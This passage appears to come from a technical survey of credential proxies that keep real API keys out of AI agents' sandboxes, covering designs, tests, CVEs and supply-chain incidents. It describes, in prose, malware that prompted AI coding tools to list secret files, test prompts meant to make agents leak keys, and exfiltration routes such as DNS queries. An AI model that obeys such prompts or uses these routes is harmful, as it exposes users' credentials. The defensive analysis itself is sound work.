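E2B lets the operator store a secret under a name such as `stripe_api_key` and use that name in network rules. Its proxy looks up the current value for each request. On Cloudflare, the operator can keep the credential in the Worker's environment or in a separate key store. Both designs let the operator replace a key without restarting the sandbox, and Docker now allows this for all service secrets, including global ones, on local machines. Hosted storage requires the operator to trust the platform, which may hold keys for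 many customers.

In April 2026, Infisical released Agent Vault, an open-source proxy with its own store of secrets. The company later concluded that it had combined two separate jobs, and that customers needed one place to manage their secrets. Agent Vault's successor, Agent Proxy, stores nothing and fetches credentials from Infisical's main secrets manager. Infisical has since reused the name Agent Vault for the product with access bundles, which Infisical's *Agent Vault* describes as a preview.

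Infisical recommends running the proxy on a different machine from the agent. The agent and the proxy then have separate identities, and only the proxy's identity can read secret values. Infisical also offers a local mode for Agent Proxy, in which the program that launches the agent fetches the real values. According to Infisical, the values stay in that program's memory and never reach the disk or the agent. Local mode is convenient on a laptop, but it puts the credentials on the same machine as the agent, so protecting them depends more on the sandbox. The newer Agent Vault does not provide a sandbox.

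### A request through Tokenizer

Fly.io's Tokenizer, from July 2023, needs no central store because the client carries the credential in encrypted form. According to *Tokenized Tokens*, an ordinary secrets manager was not enough because an attacker who took over Fly.io's web application could read any bearer token that the application could read from the manager.

Tokenizer has a pair of keys: a public key that encrypts and a private key that decrypts. To prepare the ticket credential, the operator encrypts it with the public key, together with the rules for its use. In simplified form, the content is:

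```
{
  "credential":    "k-51f0c2e97a",
  "allowed_hosts": ["api.tickets.example"],
  "client_check":  "hash of the client's password"
}
```

The encrypted result is the only version that the client receives. To file a ticket, it sends this request to Tokenizer:

```
POST http://api.tickets.example/v1/tickets HTTP/1.1
Host: api.tickets.example
Proxy-Tokenizer: q8Zt...w3E=
Proxy-Authorization: Bearer client-password
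Content-Type: application/json
Content-Length: 29

{"title":"Login page broken"}
```

Tokenizer then handles it as follows:

1. It decrypts the value in the `Proxy-Tokenizer` header with its private key.
2. It checks the client's password against the hash, and the destination against the list of allowed hosts.
3. It removes the two proxy headers and adds `Authorization: Bearer k-51f0c2e97a`.
4. It sends the request to the ticket service over TLS.

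The client sends requests to Tokenizer over plain HTTP, so the proxy can read them without intercepting TLS, and the client doesn't have to trust an extra certificate authority. The connection carries the client's password and the content of the request, so it needs some other protection, such as a private network.

An attacker who controls the client can copy the encrypted value but can't add a host to its list, since Tokenizer can't decrypt a value that someone has altered. The operator can't edit the list in place either, so adding a host requires encrypting the credential again and replacing the client's copy. Anyone who obtains Tokenizer's private key can decrypt every credential encrypted for that proxy.

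Tokenizer is less convenient for AI agents because their tools would have to add the `Proxy-Tokenizer` header to their requests, whereas an unmodified SDK can use an ordinary surrogate as its key.

### Host scopes and default network access

With most of these systems, the operator writes the host scope. For its built-in services, Docker supplies one. Four of the eleven services have a single host, while others have several:

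| Docker service | Hosts that receive the credential |
|---|---|
| `mistral` | `api.mistral.ai` |
| `anthropic` | `api.anthropic.com`, `console.anthropic.com`, `claude.ai`, `mcp-proxy.anthropic.com` |
| `openai` | `api.openai.com`, `openai.com`, `chatgpt.com`, `www.chatgpt.com` |
| `github` | `github.com`, `api.github.com`, `gist.github.com`, `raw.githubusercontent.com`, `api.githubcopilot.com`, `copilot.github.com` |

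A ready-made list saves the user from writing a pattern that is too broad, but it may include hosts the agent doesn't need or omit ones it does. An agent that only opens issues needs `api.github.com`, yet the proxy also authenticates its requests to `gist.github.com` if the network policy allows them. An agent that installs private npm packages from GitHub needs `npm.pkg.github.com`, which isn't on the list, so the user has to add a custom secret for it.

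Docker's secrets are available to every sandbox unless the user limits them to one, so a GitHub token stored for one project can authenticate an agent working on another. Infisical instead requires the operator to grant an agent specific bundles.

Until version 0.51.0 in November 2026, Docker's proxy substituted custom secrets even if they had no destination hosts. Docker lists the change as breaking in its release notes and tells users to add hosts to such secrets.

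E2B, like Deno, leaves outbound network access open until the operator restricts it, so by default it protects only the credentials. Vercel can inject credentials while allowing traffic to every other domain, so its users can also end up protecting only the credentials. On Cloudflare, setting `allowedHosts` blocks every host not on the list.

Docker asks the user to choose a network policy at first run. Version 0.32.0 made the "balanced" preset the highlighted option, so pressing Enter accepts it. Later release notes mention an implicit rule that denies anything no other rule allows. Judging by these notes, Docker has moved away from the permissive policy it documented in March.

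An allowlist can also permit traffic to addresses it doesn't list. When an operator allows a domain on E2B, the firewall also allows all traffic to 8.8.8.8, Google's public DNS server, so that programs can look up names. Adding that address to the deny list doesn't block it. A compromised container could therefore leak data through DNS queries.

E2B describes public DNS servers as a gap and offers two alternatives. The operator can run a private DNS server, or allow no DNS servers and list the required hostnames in the container's `/etc/hosts` file. Requests to allowed hosts still work with the file because E2B routes them by name. Listing names this way is practical for an agent that calls three APIs, but less so for one that installs packages from many sites.

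Cloudflare goes furthest in separating sandboxes from each other. It creates a certificate authority for each sandbox, so a stolen private key would work against only that sandbox. The key never leaves a helper process outside the sandbox. E2B creates one certificate authority for each physical node, so sandboxes on the same node may share it, and a stolen key would work against all that do.

Sharing a certificate authority can also break connections. If a paused E2B sandbox resumes on another node, its authority may change, and a program that loaded the old certificate at startup will reject connections until it loads the new one or restarts.

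A Cloudflare Worker can also use the sandbox's identifier to look up a credential for that sandbox alone. An operator with two customers could give each customer's agent a different key for the same service, without putting an identifying password in the container.

Both Cloudflare and Docker can reduce access after setup. Cloudflare's example allows `github.com` and `npmjs.org` while the sandbox installs packages, then blocks HTTP traffic. With Docker, a developer who packages an agent can mark a credential as needed only during installation, and the proxy stops supplying it to the installation hosts before the agent starts. A package's install script can still misuse the credential during setup.

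### Random, realistic and readable surrogates

Deno's surrogates begin with `DENO_SECRET_PLACEHOLDER_`, followed by a long random string. Novita, another sandbox provider, uses `novita_secret_` followed by random hexadecimal digits. Someone who finds one in a log can tell which product made it but not which service it is for. Programs that check a key's format may reject these surrogates.

Docker's surrogates for custom secrets start with `sbx-cs-` by default, but the user can set a pattern such as `sk-{rand}` to imitate an OpenAI key. Surrogates that imitate real keys, as Airut's do, pass more format checks but are more likely to set off scanners for leaked keys.

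microsandbox uses readable surrogates such as `$MSB_OPENAI_API_KEY`. Its developers say this keeps automated tests stable when they compare a program's output with a saved copy, because the surrogate is the same in every run. However, if a script passes the surrogate to a second shell as part of a command, the dollar sign may cause that shell to treat it as a variable, find no value and send an empty credential. Operators can choose a different surrogate, according to microsandbox's *Secrets*.

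Whether a surrogate must be hard to guess depends on how the proxy identifies the container. If each container has its own proxy or connection, an outsider gains nothing by guessing the surrogate, so Docker can use `proxy-managed` in every sandbox. If several containers share a proxy that accepts a surrogate from any of them, one container could use another's credential by guessing a predictable surrogate.

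### The systems compared

The dates below are those of the documentation, which in Docker's case describes version 0.54.

| System | What the proxy changes | Where the real credential is | Outbound access | Value in the container | Documentation |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Docker, service secrets | Writes the authentication header | Host keychain, or a file on some Linux hosts | Chosen at first run | `proxy-managed` | November 2026 |
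| Docker, custom secrets | Swaps a surrogate in chosen headers | Same as above | Chosen at first run | `sbx-cs-` and random text, or a custom pattern | November 2026 |
| Deno | Swaps a surrogate, with no part of the request specified | Platform | Open by default | Fixed prefix and random text | January 2026 |
| Vercel | Adds or overwrites headers | Platform's network policy | Set by policy, can be fully open | None needed | Undated |
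| Cloudflare | Runs the operator's code, which can write headers | Worker's environment or a key store | Denied by default once `allowedHosts` is set | None needed | April 2026 |
| E2B | Writes headers | Platform's secret store | Open by default | None needed | Undated |
| Infisical, current Agent Vault | Writes a header or swaps a surrogate | Infisical's platform | Optional policy blocks hosts outside the bundle | Session token, plus a surrogate where needed | Undated |
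| microsandbox | Swaps a surrogate, by default only in headers | Host | Not specified with its secrets feature | Readable name, or a custom surrogate | Undated |
| Fly.io's Tokenizer | Decrypts a credential and usually writes it into a header | Encrypted, with the client | Outside its function | Encrypted credential and rules | July 2023 |

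## What controlled tests have shown

Few people have published tests of credential proxies for agents, and most of them tested systems they had built. In September 2026 Kenney and colleagues reported on their own company's product, Corvic Security Vault, which uses header injection. An operator creates a "connector" that stores a credential, the header it belongs in and the host that may receive it. Code in the sandbox gets only the connector's identifier, so it has no surrogate to send.

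### Sixteen probes of Corvic's vault

The team ran two black-box experiments on 27 September 2026 in the product's sandboxed Python environment, using only what code in the sandbox could observe. One experiment used a connector for FRED, the economic database of the Federal Reserve Bank of St. Louis, and the other a connector for GitHub. The team set a yes-or-no expectation for each of 16 probes beforehand so that they could not reinterpret an unexpected result as a success.

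The 16 probes covered seven control domains. Five probes tested whether the vault injects a credential only at its own host, and one tested whether an authorised call works. The other five domains had two probes each: the process environment, the file system, disclosure to other hosts, the calling code's view of the credential, and cloud metadata.

The design needed both positive and negative controls. A sandbox with no network connection, or a vault that never injected a key, would pass every leak test, so the positive control was an authenticated call that had to succeed. But that call would also succeed if the vault added the key to every request, whatever its destination. The negative controls ruled this out by sending requests to echo services, which return whatever request they receive, and to an unrelated API, which had to return a missing-authentication error.

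All 16 probes had the expected outcome:

| What the code tried | Result |
|---|---|
| Call GitHub's user endpoint without supplying a credential | Status 200, with an authenticated identity |
| Search 20 environment variables | No name that suggested a secret, no value that looked like a token |
| Read `/proc/self/environ` | Readable, 634 bytes, no match |
| Look in 12 common credential locations and in secret-mount folders | Nothing there |
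| Inspect its own prepared request to GitHub | No `Authorization` header |
| Call three echo services | Status 200, no `Authorization` header or token in the reply |
| Ask OpenAI's API for its list of models | Status 401, missing authentication |
| Contact the Google and AWS metadata endpoints | Both timed out after six seconds |

The last row matters because many cloud machines have a metadata address where any program can request credentials for the machine's own account. An agent that reached that address might not need the vault's key. Kenney and colleagues caution that a timeout shows only that the endpoints were unreachable during the run.

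The GitHub experiment deserves more weight than the FRED one. The FRED connector never authenticated successfully, so the absence of a key in its echo replies could mean that the vault had injected nothing anywhere. The GitHub connector worked at its own host and injected nothing at the other hosts tested, although these were only two echo services and one unrelated API.

The search for leaked keys was also fairly coarse. It checked for the prefixes of common token formats and for variable names containing words that suggest a secret, so it would have missed a key that had no known prefix and was stored under an unrelated name. Searching for the exact key would have been more conclusive, but the team had ruled out copying any secret value.

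The results on authenticated calls, host scope, stored copies and metadata are relevant to surrogate designs too, though they don't show that any other product behaves the same way. The experiments don't test the swap itself, such as whether a proxy finds the surrogate or leaves it unchanged when it appears in the wrong part of a request. Some expected outcomes would also change with a surrogate. The prepared request would have an `Authorization` header and an echo service would return it, so the tester would have to check that the value was not the real key.

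### Why the FRED connector failed

The vault's call to FRED returned status 400 and a message that the `api_key` variable was not set. FRED takes its key as a query parameter in the URL, but the connector's configuration put it in an `Authorization` header. Kenney and colleagues scored this failure separately from the security probes because it disclosed nothing.

A surrogate could have prevented this mistake. FRED's client library would have put the surrogate in the query string, and a proxy that searches the URL could have replaced it with the real key there, but a proxy that swaps only in headers would have forwarded the surrogate unchanged, and FRED would have rejected it. With either kind of proxy, the operator has to know how each service accepts its key.

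### Risk scores and untested attacks

Kenney and colleagues also scored eight threats before and after adding the vault. Each score multiplies a likelihood from 1 to 5 by an impact from 1 to 5:

| Threat | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Secret pasted into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
| Indirect prompt injection | 25 | 12 |
| Credential sent to another host | 20 | 4 |
| Credential found in the running environment | 20 | 4 |
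| Over-privileged connector | 20 | 15 |
| Replay of a long-lived token | 20 | 8 |
| Leak through telemetry or errors | 16 | 8 |
| Misconfigured connector | 9 | 6 |

These scores are expert judgements by the vendor's employees, and a fall from 25 to 12 does not mean that the risk has halved. The 16 probes are relevant mainly to two rows, the credential sent to another host and the credential found in the running environment. The score of 4 for pasted secrets assumes that users stop pasting them, which a vault can encourage but not enforce.

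The two highest remaining scores are more persuasive because they are unfavorable to the product. The score for an over-privileged connector falls only from 20 to 15, and the score for prompt injection remains at 12, because the vault does not limit what the agent does with a credential. Kenney and colleagues suggest running an established prompt-injection benchmark against a vault, which would replace this estimate with a measurement.

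The experiments did not test several attacks that matter for any credential proxy: redirects, token capture during an OAuth refresh, a hostile approved host, and DNS rebinding, in which a domain name resolves to a harmless address when the proxy checks it and a different one when the proxy connects.

The tests also did not cover MCP sessions, browser tools or heavy load on the vault, and trials were not repeated. They did not verify how Corvic encrypts stored credentials, separates its customers or keeps audit logs.

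### A test of the swap itself

Ghosh (2026), in *Tracekit Box*, tested a proxy that swaps surrogates for real keys. Tracekit Box is an open-source tool from Ghosh's company, Cygnux Labs. It runs each agent in a small virtual machine with no network card, so every connection has to pass through a proxy on the host. The machine holds a surrogate such as `tkbox_GH_` followed by 32 hexadecimal digits. The proxy replaces the surrogate with the real key only in one header and only for exact host names, and blocks the surrogate anywhere else in traffic it can read.

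All 13 of the project's end-to-end checks passed on 26 October 2026. Two tested the swap directly. In one, a test server received the real value in the `Authorization` header, while the variable inside the machine contained only the surrogate. In the other, the program put the same surrogate in an `X-Smuggle` header, and the proxy refused the request with status 403. Other checks confirmed that the machine had no external network interface and could not reach the cloud metadata address.

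Each check covers a single representative case. For wider coverage, Ghosh used fuzzing, in which a program generates large numbers of unusual inputs and tests whether the software still obeys a stated rule. One such rule was that a response must never show the virtual machine a secret that an approved host had echoed. Fuzzing produced nine findings across the whole system, all of which Ghosh reports as fixed. Four of them affected the swap or the scrubbing of responses:

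| Cause | Possible effect | Fix |
|---|---|---|
| A request inside an approved connection could name a different host in a form that the proxy's check missed | The approved service's front end could pass the real credential to another site | The proxy refuses such requests |
| The proxy did not scrub responses with a status code below 100 | The virtual machine could read a credential that the host had returned | The proxy returns an error instead |
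| The marker that replaced a credential could combine with neighbouring text | The scrubbed response could contain the credential again | Markers can no longer form part of a match |
| The scrubber read a response in pieces and mishandled a secret that contained another secret | Parts of the longer secret could remain in the response | Ghosh lists it as fixed |

Ghosh considers the misnamed host the most serious of the four flaws. The proxy had correctly verified the connection's destination and would have recorded only the approved host, yet the credential could have gone elsewhere. The other three matter only if an approved host returns the credential, but they show how hard it is to remove credentials from responses reliably, even with code written for that purpose.

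Three rounds of independent review before the project's release found similar problems. Ghosh reports these reviews in the developer's own paper, so they are weaker evidence than an audit published by the reviewers. The tests are easier to trust because the code is public and anyone can rerun them. The paper's comparison with rival products is less reliable because it marks E2B, microsandbox and OpenShell as unable to keep keys out of the sandbox, which contradicts their documentation.

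None of these tests involved a capable agent instructed to escape. They used scripted attacks, which can confirm that a known defence works but are less likely to reveal an unexpected way around it.

### A comparison with directly readable keys

In *CapSeal*, Jin, Guo and Cheung (2026) compared agents that hold their keys with agents that use a broker. The test prompts tried to make the agent reveal its key or use it outside its permitted scope. With CapSeal, the team's research prototype, the agent asks for permission to perform a particular action. The broker then builds the request, adds the key and sends it, so there is no surrogate to swap.

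| Outcome over HTTP | Two systems with direct keys | CapSeal |
|---|---|---|
| Key appeared in output the agent could see | 100% of trials | 0% |
| Authenticated action outside the permitted scope succeeded | 0% | 0% |
| Legitimate request completed | 100% | 100% |

The first row supports keeping keys out of the agent's reach. The 100% figure comes from scripted trials with fixed prompts, so it doesn't estimate how often real agents disclose their keys. No system leaked a key in the equivalent SSH tests, so those results can't show any benefit from the broker.

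The misuse row also gives no evidence that the broker prevented an unauthorised action, because the systems with direct keys allowed none either. The 95% confidence interval is 0 to 3.7%, which corresponds to about 100 trials per system. A more useful test would include an attack that succeeds against the baseline.

### How much delay a proxy adds

No published measurement from 2025 or 2026 appears to isolate the delay that a surrogate-swapping proxy adds. Ghosh did not benchmark Tracekit Box, but its swap check took 0.10 seconds in one run, including the time to run a command in the virtual machine, so the swap itself took at most that long.

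Measurements of related systems give a rough idea of what to expect:

- **CapSeal** added a median of 0.149 milliseconds to an HTTP request and 0.208 milliseconds to an SSH command. Jin and colleagues made 500 measurements of each against local targets. The broker creates its own requests, so these figures include no TLS interception.
- **A relay for calls to language models** added a median of 3.7 milliseconds as an ordinary process, according to *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (2026). Running it in an enclave, a protected area that the rest of the machine can't read, raised this to 5.7 milliseconds. The test used small requests, a local server and connections that were already open.
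- **A broker that creates temporary credentials** added 28.2 milliseconds to changes in Kubernetes, which manages containers, and 136.9 milliseconds to changes in AWS firewall rules, according to *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026). It also checks the system's current state and writes each operation to a database.

A plain swap does much less work than the last of these systems, so its delay is probably closer to the relay's. That delay would hardly matter for an agent, because the time a model takes to start answering varies by hundreds of milliseconds. But an interception proxy has to set up two TLS connections, so a program that opens a new connection for every request could have longer delays than the relay's figures suggest.

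### Published vulnerabilities

No independent test or security audit of a surrogate-swapping proxy appears to have been published in 2025 or 2026. Public vulnerability records provide some independent evidence, since outsiders found some of the flaws they list.

According to stack.watch, a site that collects vulnerability records, Docker's proxy could forward a credential supplied by the container alongside the one it had injected. The cause was an incomplete rule for removing alternative credentials. The real key stayed out of the container, but a service that preferred the container's credential could have carried out the request under somebody else's account, which overwriting a header is supposed to prevent. The record is dated 8 October 2026 and rates the severity at 5.9 out of 10.

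Another flaw let data leave Docker's sandboxes because the network allowlist covered web traffic but not DNS queries (OSV, *Docker Sandboxes network egress allowlist bypass via unfiltered DNS resolution*, 2026). An outsider found the flaw, according to Docker (2026). Docker itself found that a block on ICMP, the protocol behind the `ping` command, could lapse after its background process restarted. Both records refer to the release notes for version 0.33.0, which presumably contains the fixes. Neither flaw exposed a credential held by the proxy.

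stack.watch lists a flaw for 3 November in Docker's `sbx cp` command, which copies files between host and sandbox. The command did not safely handle links in a shared folder. If a malicious sandbox replaced such a link and a user then ran the command, it could copy a host file from outside the folder into the sandbox. On a Linux server where Docker keeps credentials in an ordinary file, this might have exposed them to the sandbox.

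NVIDIA disclosed two relevant flaws in OpenShell on 25 August 2026. *CVE-2026-65085 Detail* (2026), from the US government's National Vulnerability Database, describes incorrect output encoding in OpenShell's inference proxy, which handles calls to AI models. The flaw might allow information disclosure and data tampering, but the record does not mention credentials.

The other flaw let code escape from the sandbox. CERT.hr, Croatia's computer emergency response team, rates it 9.9 out of 10 in *CVE-2026-65093* (2026). After an escape, even a correct token swap might not have protected credentials on the same host. In *NVIDIA security advisory (AV26-849)* (2026), the Canadian Centre for Cyber Security told OpenShell users to install the updates.

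## What has been observed in real deployments

Field reports show fairly clearly where people leave agents' credentials and how attackers collect them, but they contain much less about proxies that swap surrogates for real keys. No public report from 2025 or 2026 appears to describe an attacker who took over a container, found only surrogates and left without a usable key. Such an attack exposes no real credentials, so people have little reason to write about it.

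### Nine agents at a healthcare company

*Caging the Agents* (Maiti, 2026) describes nine AI agents in production at a healthcare technology company whose subsidiaries serve large hospital networks. The paper assesses Maiti's own architecture. Maiti is an executive at Commure, a health technology company, and also runs a security firm. The agents ran on OpenClaw, an open-source framework that gives each agent a shell and lets it install packages and send messages. Each agent had its own virtual machine.

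The agents needed keys for services such as GitHub, Slack and AWS Bedrock. OpenClaw stores these in `.env` files and a configuration file, `openclaw.json`. Some machines also exported keys in `.bashrc`, a script that sets up a user's shell. On 11 March 2026, another AI agent, built for auditing, searched all nine machines and found problems on three:

| Machine | Finding | Severity | Status |
|---|---|---|---|
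| Galadriel | 12 credentials exported in `.bashrc` | High | Fixed the same day |
| Galadriel | Any account on the machine could read `openclaw.json` | High | Fixed the same day |
| Boromir | Any account on the machine could read `openclaw.json` | High | Fixed the same day |
| Gandalf | AWS Bedrock key exported in `.bashrc` | High | Fixed the same day |
| Gandalf | `.env` files scattered through the workspace | Medium | Open |
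| Boromir | `.env` file with tokens in the workspace | Medium | Open |

To fix the high-severity problems, automated procedures removed the keys from `.bashrc` and restricted the configuration files to their owner. A follow-up check found the four problems gone.

This clean-up probably left the keys within the agents' reach. The procedures saved backups of the shell files, and those backups would still contain the keys unless somebody edited them. Maiti describes the repairs without mentioning that any key was replaced. The agents' commands could also still read `openclaw.json`, because they normally run under the account that owns the file.

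Maiti's longer-term remedy is a credential proxy in a sidecar, a second container beside the agent's. The agent sends a model request to `localhost:8443/v1/messages` without a key, and the sidecar adds the key and forwards the request to `api.anthropic.com`. This is header injection, so the agent's container holds no surrogate credential. The sidecar also limits the rate, size and destination of requests.

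Maiti writes that the sidecar eliminates the kind of exposure found in the audit. This follows from the design for any key that exists only in the sidecar, but the paper's measurements do not test it. In the abstract, Maiti describes the architecture as deployed, but a later section describes it as the "current migration target", and the audited machines still kept their keys in files. The before-and-after results therefore measure the clean-up of those files. Maiti reports no attack on the proxy and no second audit after the migration. The paper refers to a 90-day deployment, but its dated steps cover only 36 days, from 3 February to 11 March.

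The planned network rules let security-audit agents contact Google Cloud's metadata endpoint, where an agent might get a real credential without going through the sidecar. Corvic's sandbox could not reach this kind of address in its tests.

### Keys taken from developers' machines and build jobs

In August 2025, attackers published malicious versions of Nx, a build tool with millions of weekly downloads. The attack lasted about 5 hours and 20 minutes, according to StepSecurity (2025). The malware posted what it stole to public GitHub repositories, so outsiders could count the credentials. GitGuardian's *The Nx s1ngularity attack* (2025) found 2,349 distinct secrets from 1,079 systems, about half of them still valid. The secrets came from environment variables, SSH key files, cryptocurrency wallets and the login files of developer tools.

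The malware also instructed AI coding tools on victims' machines to list files that might contain secrets. GitGuardian found that it targeted these tools on 366 systems and that 95 of them, about a quarter, produced the list. GitGuardian attributes many of the failures to refusals by the tools, but an operator can't rely on a model to refuse.

Most victims were probably working on their own computers, since 85% of the infected systems ran macOS. Nothing in the reports suggests that they used credential proxies. If the ticket-filing agent had installed Nx in its container, the malware would have found a surrogate in `TICKET_KEY`, but it could still have published the agent's source code. According to GitLab's *CVE-2025-10894* (2025), the malware posted its findings to a repository under the victim's own GitHub account. If the agent had also held a surrogate for a GitHub token that could create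 repositories, the proxy would have authenticated that upload.

On 28 August, attackers used the stolen GitHub tokens to make private repositories public. GitGuardian counted 10,767 of these repositories, which contained 82,901 secrets, 11,168 of them valid. Surrogates would have been more useful here, because a surrogate copied from a container the day before would not have worked at GitHub. But the malware could have made the repositories public while it was running inside the container, unless the token lacked that permission or the proxy refused the request.

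A larger attack in 2025, Shai-Hulud 2, also spread through npm packages. GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026) analysed data stolen in the attack from 6,943 machines and found 33,185 unique secrets, at least 3,760 of which were still valid. Build runners, which compile and test software automatically, made up 59% of the machines. About 44% of the machines held more than ten secrets, according to the histogram on GitGuardian's website, although the report's text gives about 30%.

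On average, each valid secret appeared in about eight places on the same machine, including shell profiles, build outputs and tool caches. An operator who replaces one environment variable with a surrogate may therefore leave about seven other copies, which the agent can still read if the operator shares the folders that hold them.

GitGuardian considers its Shai-Hulud figures conservative, partly because the malware did not search the folders where agents keep their memory. It later reported an average of roughly 150 secrets per developer machine in an early-access programme, with about 40% of the high-risk and critical ones in AI tools' folders and log files (McDaniel, 2026, *GitGuardian's Mixin Kit extends Docker Sandboxes for safer AI coding*). The participants may not be typical, and GitGuardian sells products that find such secrets.

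### Malware that requests new credentials

On 17 November 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of `agent-framework`, Microsoft's official Python package for building AI agents. PyPI, the main public registry for Python packages, removed one after 31 minutes and the other after about eight. TechRadar's *Microsoft's official Agent Framework Python package on PyPI hijacked* (2026) estimates around 150 downloads of the two versions, based on the package's usual download rate. Nobody has confirmed how many credentials the attackers obtained, if any.

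Help Net Security's *Credential stealer slipped into Microsoft’s official Python agent framework* (2026) lists what the code tried to collect. Besides searching for stored keys, it asked cloud services for new ones. A container with surrogates would have protected some of these credentials but not others:

| What the code tried to collect | What it would have found in a container with surrogates |
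|---|---|
| Environment variables with names such as `TOKEN` or `SECRET` | Surrogates, for every key the operator had registered |
| The environments of up to 300 other processes | Surrogates, if the proxy and its secrets were outside the container |
| `.env` files and the login files of Git, Docker and cloud tools | Any real keys that the operator had left in those files |
| New tokens from Azure and from build services | Real tokens, if the container could reach those services and had permission to request them |

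StepSecurity, one of three security companies that caught the attack, cautions that the code tried to request tokens but may not have received any. The operator can prevent such requests only by removing the machine's permission to make them or blocking the address they are sent to.

The code sent everything it collected to an address at `webhook.site`, a public service for receiving web requests. In an agent's container, a network allowlist that omitted this host would have blocked the upload. A swapping proxy would have been a second defence for registered keys.

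### LiteLLM and the risk of storing keys in one place

LiteLLM is open-source software that gives programs a single interface to many AI models. It can run as a library inside a program or as a gateway, a separate server that stores the API keys and forwards requests to the model providers. Attackers compromised its releases twice in 2026.

On 24 March, two malicious versions of LiteLLM were available on PyPI for about 40 minutes. According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), these versions searched for environment variables, SSH keys, cloud credentials, Kubernetes tokens and database passwords, and sent them to `models.litellm.cloud`, a domain LiteLLM does not own. *LiteLLM Supply-Chain Attack Exposed Credentials Across 2,500 Organizations* (Ofonagoro, 2026) reports that the theft may also have exposed hundreds of thousands of build pipelines. Both figures measure possible exposure, and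 there is no confirmed count of stolen credentials.

In an agent's container, surrogates would have protected the API keys in environment variables, and an allowlist would probably have blocked the unfamiliar domain. The database passwords and SSH keys would have needed other protection, because programs do not normally send them in HTTP requests that a proxy can edit.

On 21 October, attackers published another malicious release of LiteLLM, version 1.107.0. *Popular AI tool LiteLLM says unrevoked key allowed hackers to target users* (Martin, 2026) reports that it was downloaded about 49,000 times, according to the security company Wiz. Downloads can include automated copies, so the number of victims may be much lower, and no total for stolen credentials is available. *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year* (Help Net Security, 2026) reports that the attacker began testing stolen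 AWS keys about four and a half hours after the data left victims' systems, to see which AI models the keys could access. With a signing proxy like OpenShell's, the malware would have found only placeholder keys in the container, and those tests would have failed.

Wang (2026), in *The attack chain behind the v1.107.0 LiteLLM release*, traces the LiteLLM breach to a master key that the team had committed to a public repository in May. The key gave access to an internal platform for running AI agents. Martin reports that the team noticed the mistake and removed the file but never revoked the key.

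The Vanguard USA's *How one unrevoked key let attackers poison LiteLLM* (2026) describes a platform whose agents filed pull requests using a GitHub token that belonged to the organisation's owner and had full permissions. On 10 October an attacker extracted this token and gained control of all LiteLLM's repositories. The attacker then obtained two engineers' tokens and used one to start a malicious release and the other to approve it.

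Surrogates might not have prevented this. Someone with the platform's master key could perhaps have read the real token from the platform's storage, or started an agent and used the token through it. A token that could only open pull requests would have limited the damage in both cases. Surrogates would have been more useful if the token had leaked through a log, as LiteLLM first suspected. LiteLLM had seen Claude Code include a user's GitHub token in text that the gateway logged. An agent with a surrogate would have put only the surrogate in that log.

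The malware also tried to read the database where LiteLLM gateways store providers' keys. Socket, a security company that analysed the code, cautions that this shows what the attackers intended but doesn't prove they succeeded. The attempt still illustrates a weakness of any design that moves real keys out of agents' containers. Withholding real keys from agents doesn't help if the attacker's code runs in the gateway.

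A break-in at a similar service may have exposed stored keys. *AIコーディングのAPIキーが狙われている* (一色, 2026), a Japanese article on the theft of API keys from AI coding tools, describes the incident at OpenCode Console, which stores users' keys for AI services and relays their requests. On 17 October the service's operator announced that someone had accessed an old system it was retiring and that stored keys might have leaked. The operator said the incident affected 1.4% of Console users. Some people reported charges they did not recognise, in some cases for hundreds of dollars, but these reports come from users, not from the operator's investigation.

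Hosted platforms that store many customers' credentials face a risk similar to that of LiteLLM's gateway and OpenCode Console, although neither of those is a sandbox proxy like the ones Airut and Docker run. A proxy on one developer's laptop is a less valuable target because a successful attack exposes only that developer's keys.

### Leaked secrets in public code

In the latest large measurement of leaked secrets, published in March 2026, GitGuardian found 28.65 million new secrets in public GitHub commits during 2025, 34% more than in 2024.

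GitGuardian's scanner recognises keys with known formats by their text. For passwords and other secrets without a fixed format, it also uses machine learning to remove false matches. GitGuardian applied its latest filter to data going back to 2021, so the change of filter does not explain the increase. It also excluded repositories with abnormally high numbers of secrets.

The total shows how often secrets reach public code, but it has several limits as evidence about agents:

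- It excludes private repositories. GitGuardian found secrets in 32.2% of the internal repositories it monitored, compared with 5.6% of public ones.
- The filter can remove real secrets along with false matches, and GitGuardian can't check whether many of the remaining ones work.
- The number of public commits grew by 43%, faster than the number of secrets, so the average commit contained slightly fewer secrets than the year before.
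- The total doesn't identify which secrets came from an agent's container.

The figures closest to agents' own work come from commits that list Claude Code as a co-author. GitGuardian reports that 3.2% of these leaked a secret, compared with 1.5% of all public commits. It also reports that Claude Code's rate peaked at 31 secrets per 1,000 commits in August and fell to 13 by December, about the same as for human authors. These figures are hard to reconcile, because the 3.2% average for the year is higher than the peak month's 3.1%. Claude Code's commits were also about twice as long for much of the year, so each had more text that could contain a secret. The data therefore can't show whether the agent handled secrets worse than people did.

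GitGuardian also found 24,008 unique secrets in public configuration files for MCP servers and confirmed that 2,117 of them worked. If these files had contained surrogates, publishing them would have exposed no usable keys. But 14% of the working secrets were PostgreSQL connection strings, which include a password. An HTTP proxy can't swap these because PostgreSQL uses its own protocol.

Owners are also slow to revoke leaked keys. GitGuardian retested secrets that had been valid in 2022 and found that more than 64% still worked in January 2026. Owners may leave a real key active even after they notice a leak, as LiteLLM's team did, so this is probably the best field evidence for surrogates that expire with the container.

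### Reports from people who run such proxies

A few developers have described their own credential proxies in online discussions. These are anecdotes, and none of the developers published measurements.

One developer built a proxy that swaps credentials and used it "for a while" with Anthropic, GitHub, Gemini, AWS and Cloudflare's storage service. They reported no problems, but expected some APIs to need extra work. This is modest evidence that the design works with common services, but little evidence that it is secure, since the developer did not describe any attack.

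Another developer ran a similar proxy as a sidecar on Kubernetes. They had to redirect all traffic with firewall rules because Node.js ignored the `HTTP_PROXY` variable. Someone replied that Node.js 24 and later use it if the operator also sets `NODE_USE_ENV_PROXY=1`.

One developer, who didn't mention using a proxy, said Claude Code was "pretty aggressive" about reading `.env` and configuration files when it had access. Another kept such files encrypted with a tool called sops, which decrypts the values only when it starts a program. This developer warned that a text editor can leave a decrypted copy on the disk if it crashes while the file is open. The program still receives the real keys, so sops protects them in storage but not from code that takes over the program.

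## Comparison with environment variables and short-lived tokens

An operator can give the ticket-filing agent API access through an environment variable, a mounted file, a short-lived or narrowly scoped token, or a surrogate that a proxy swaps for the real key. The table compares these options for a container that runs unreviewed code.

| Question | Real key in an environment variable | Real key in a mounted file | Short-lived or narrow token in the container | Surrogate with a swapping proxy |
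|---|---|---|---|---|
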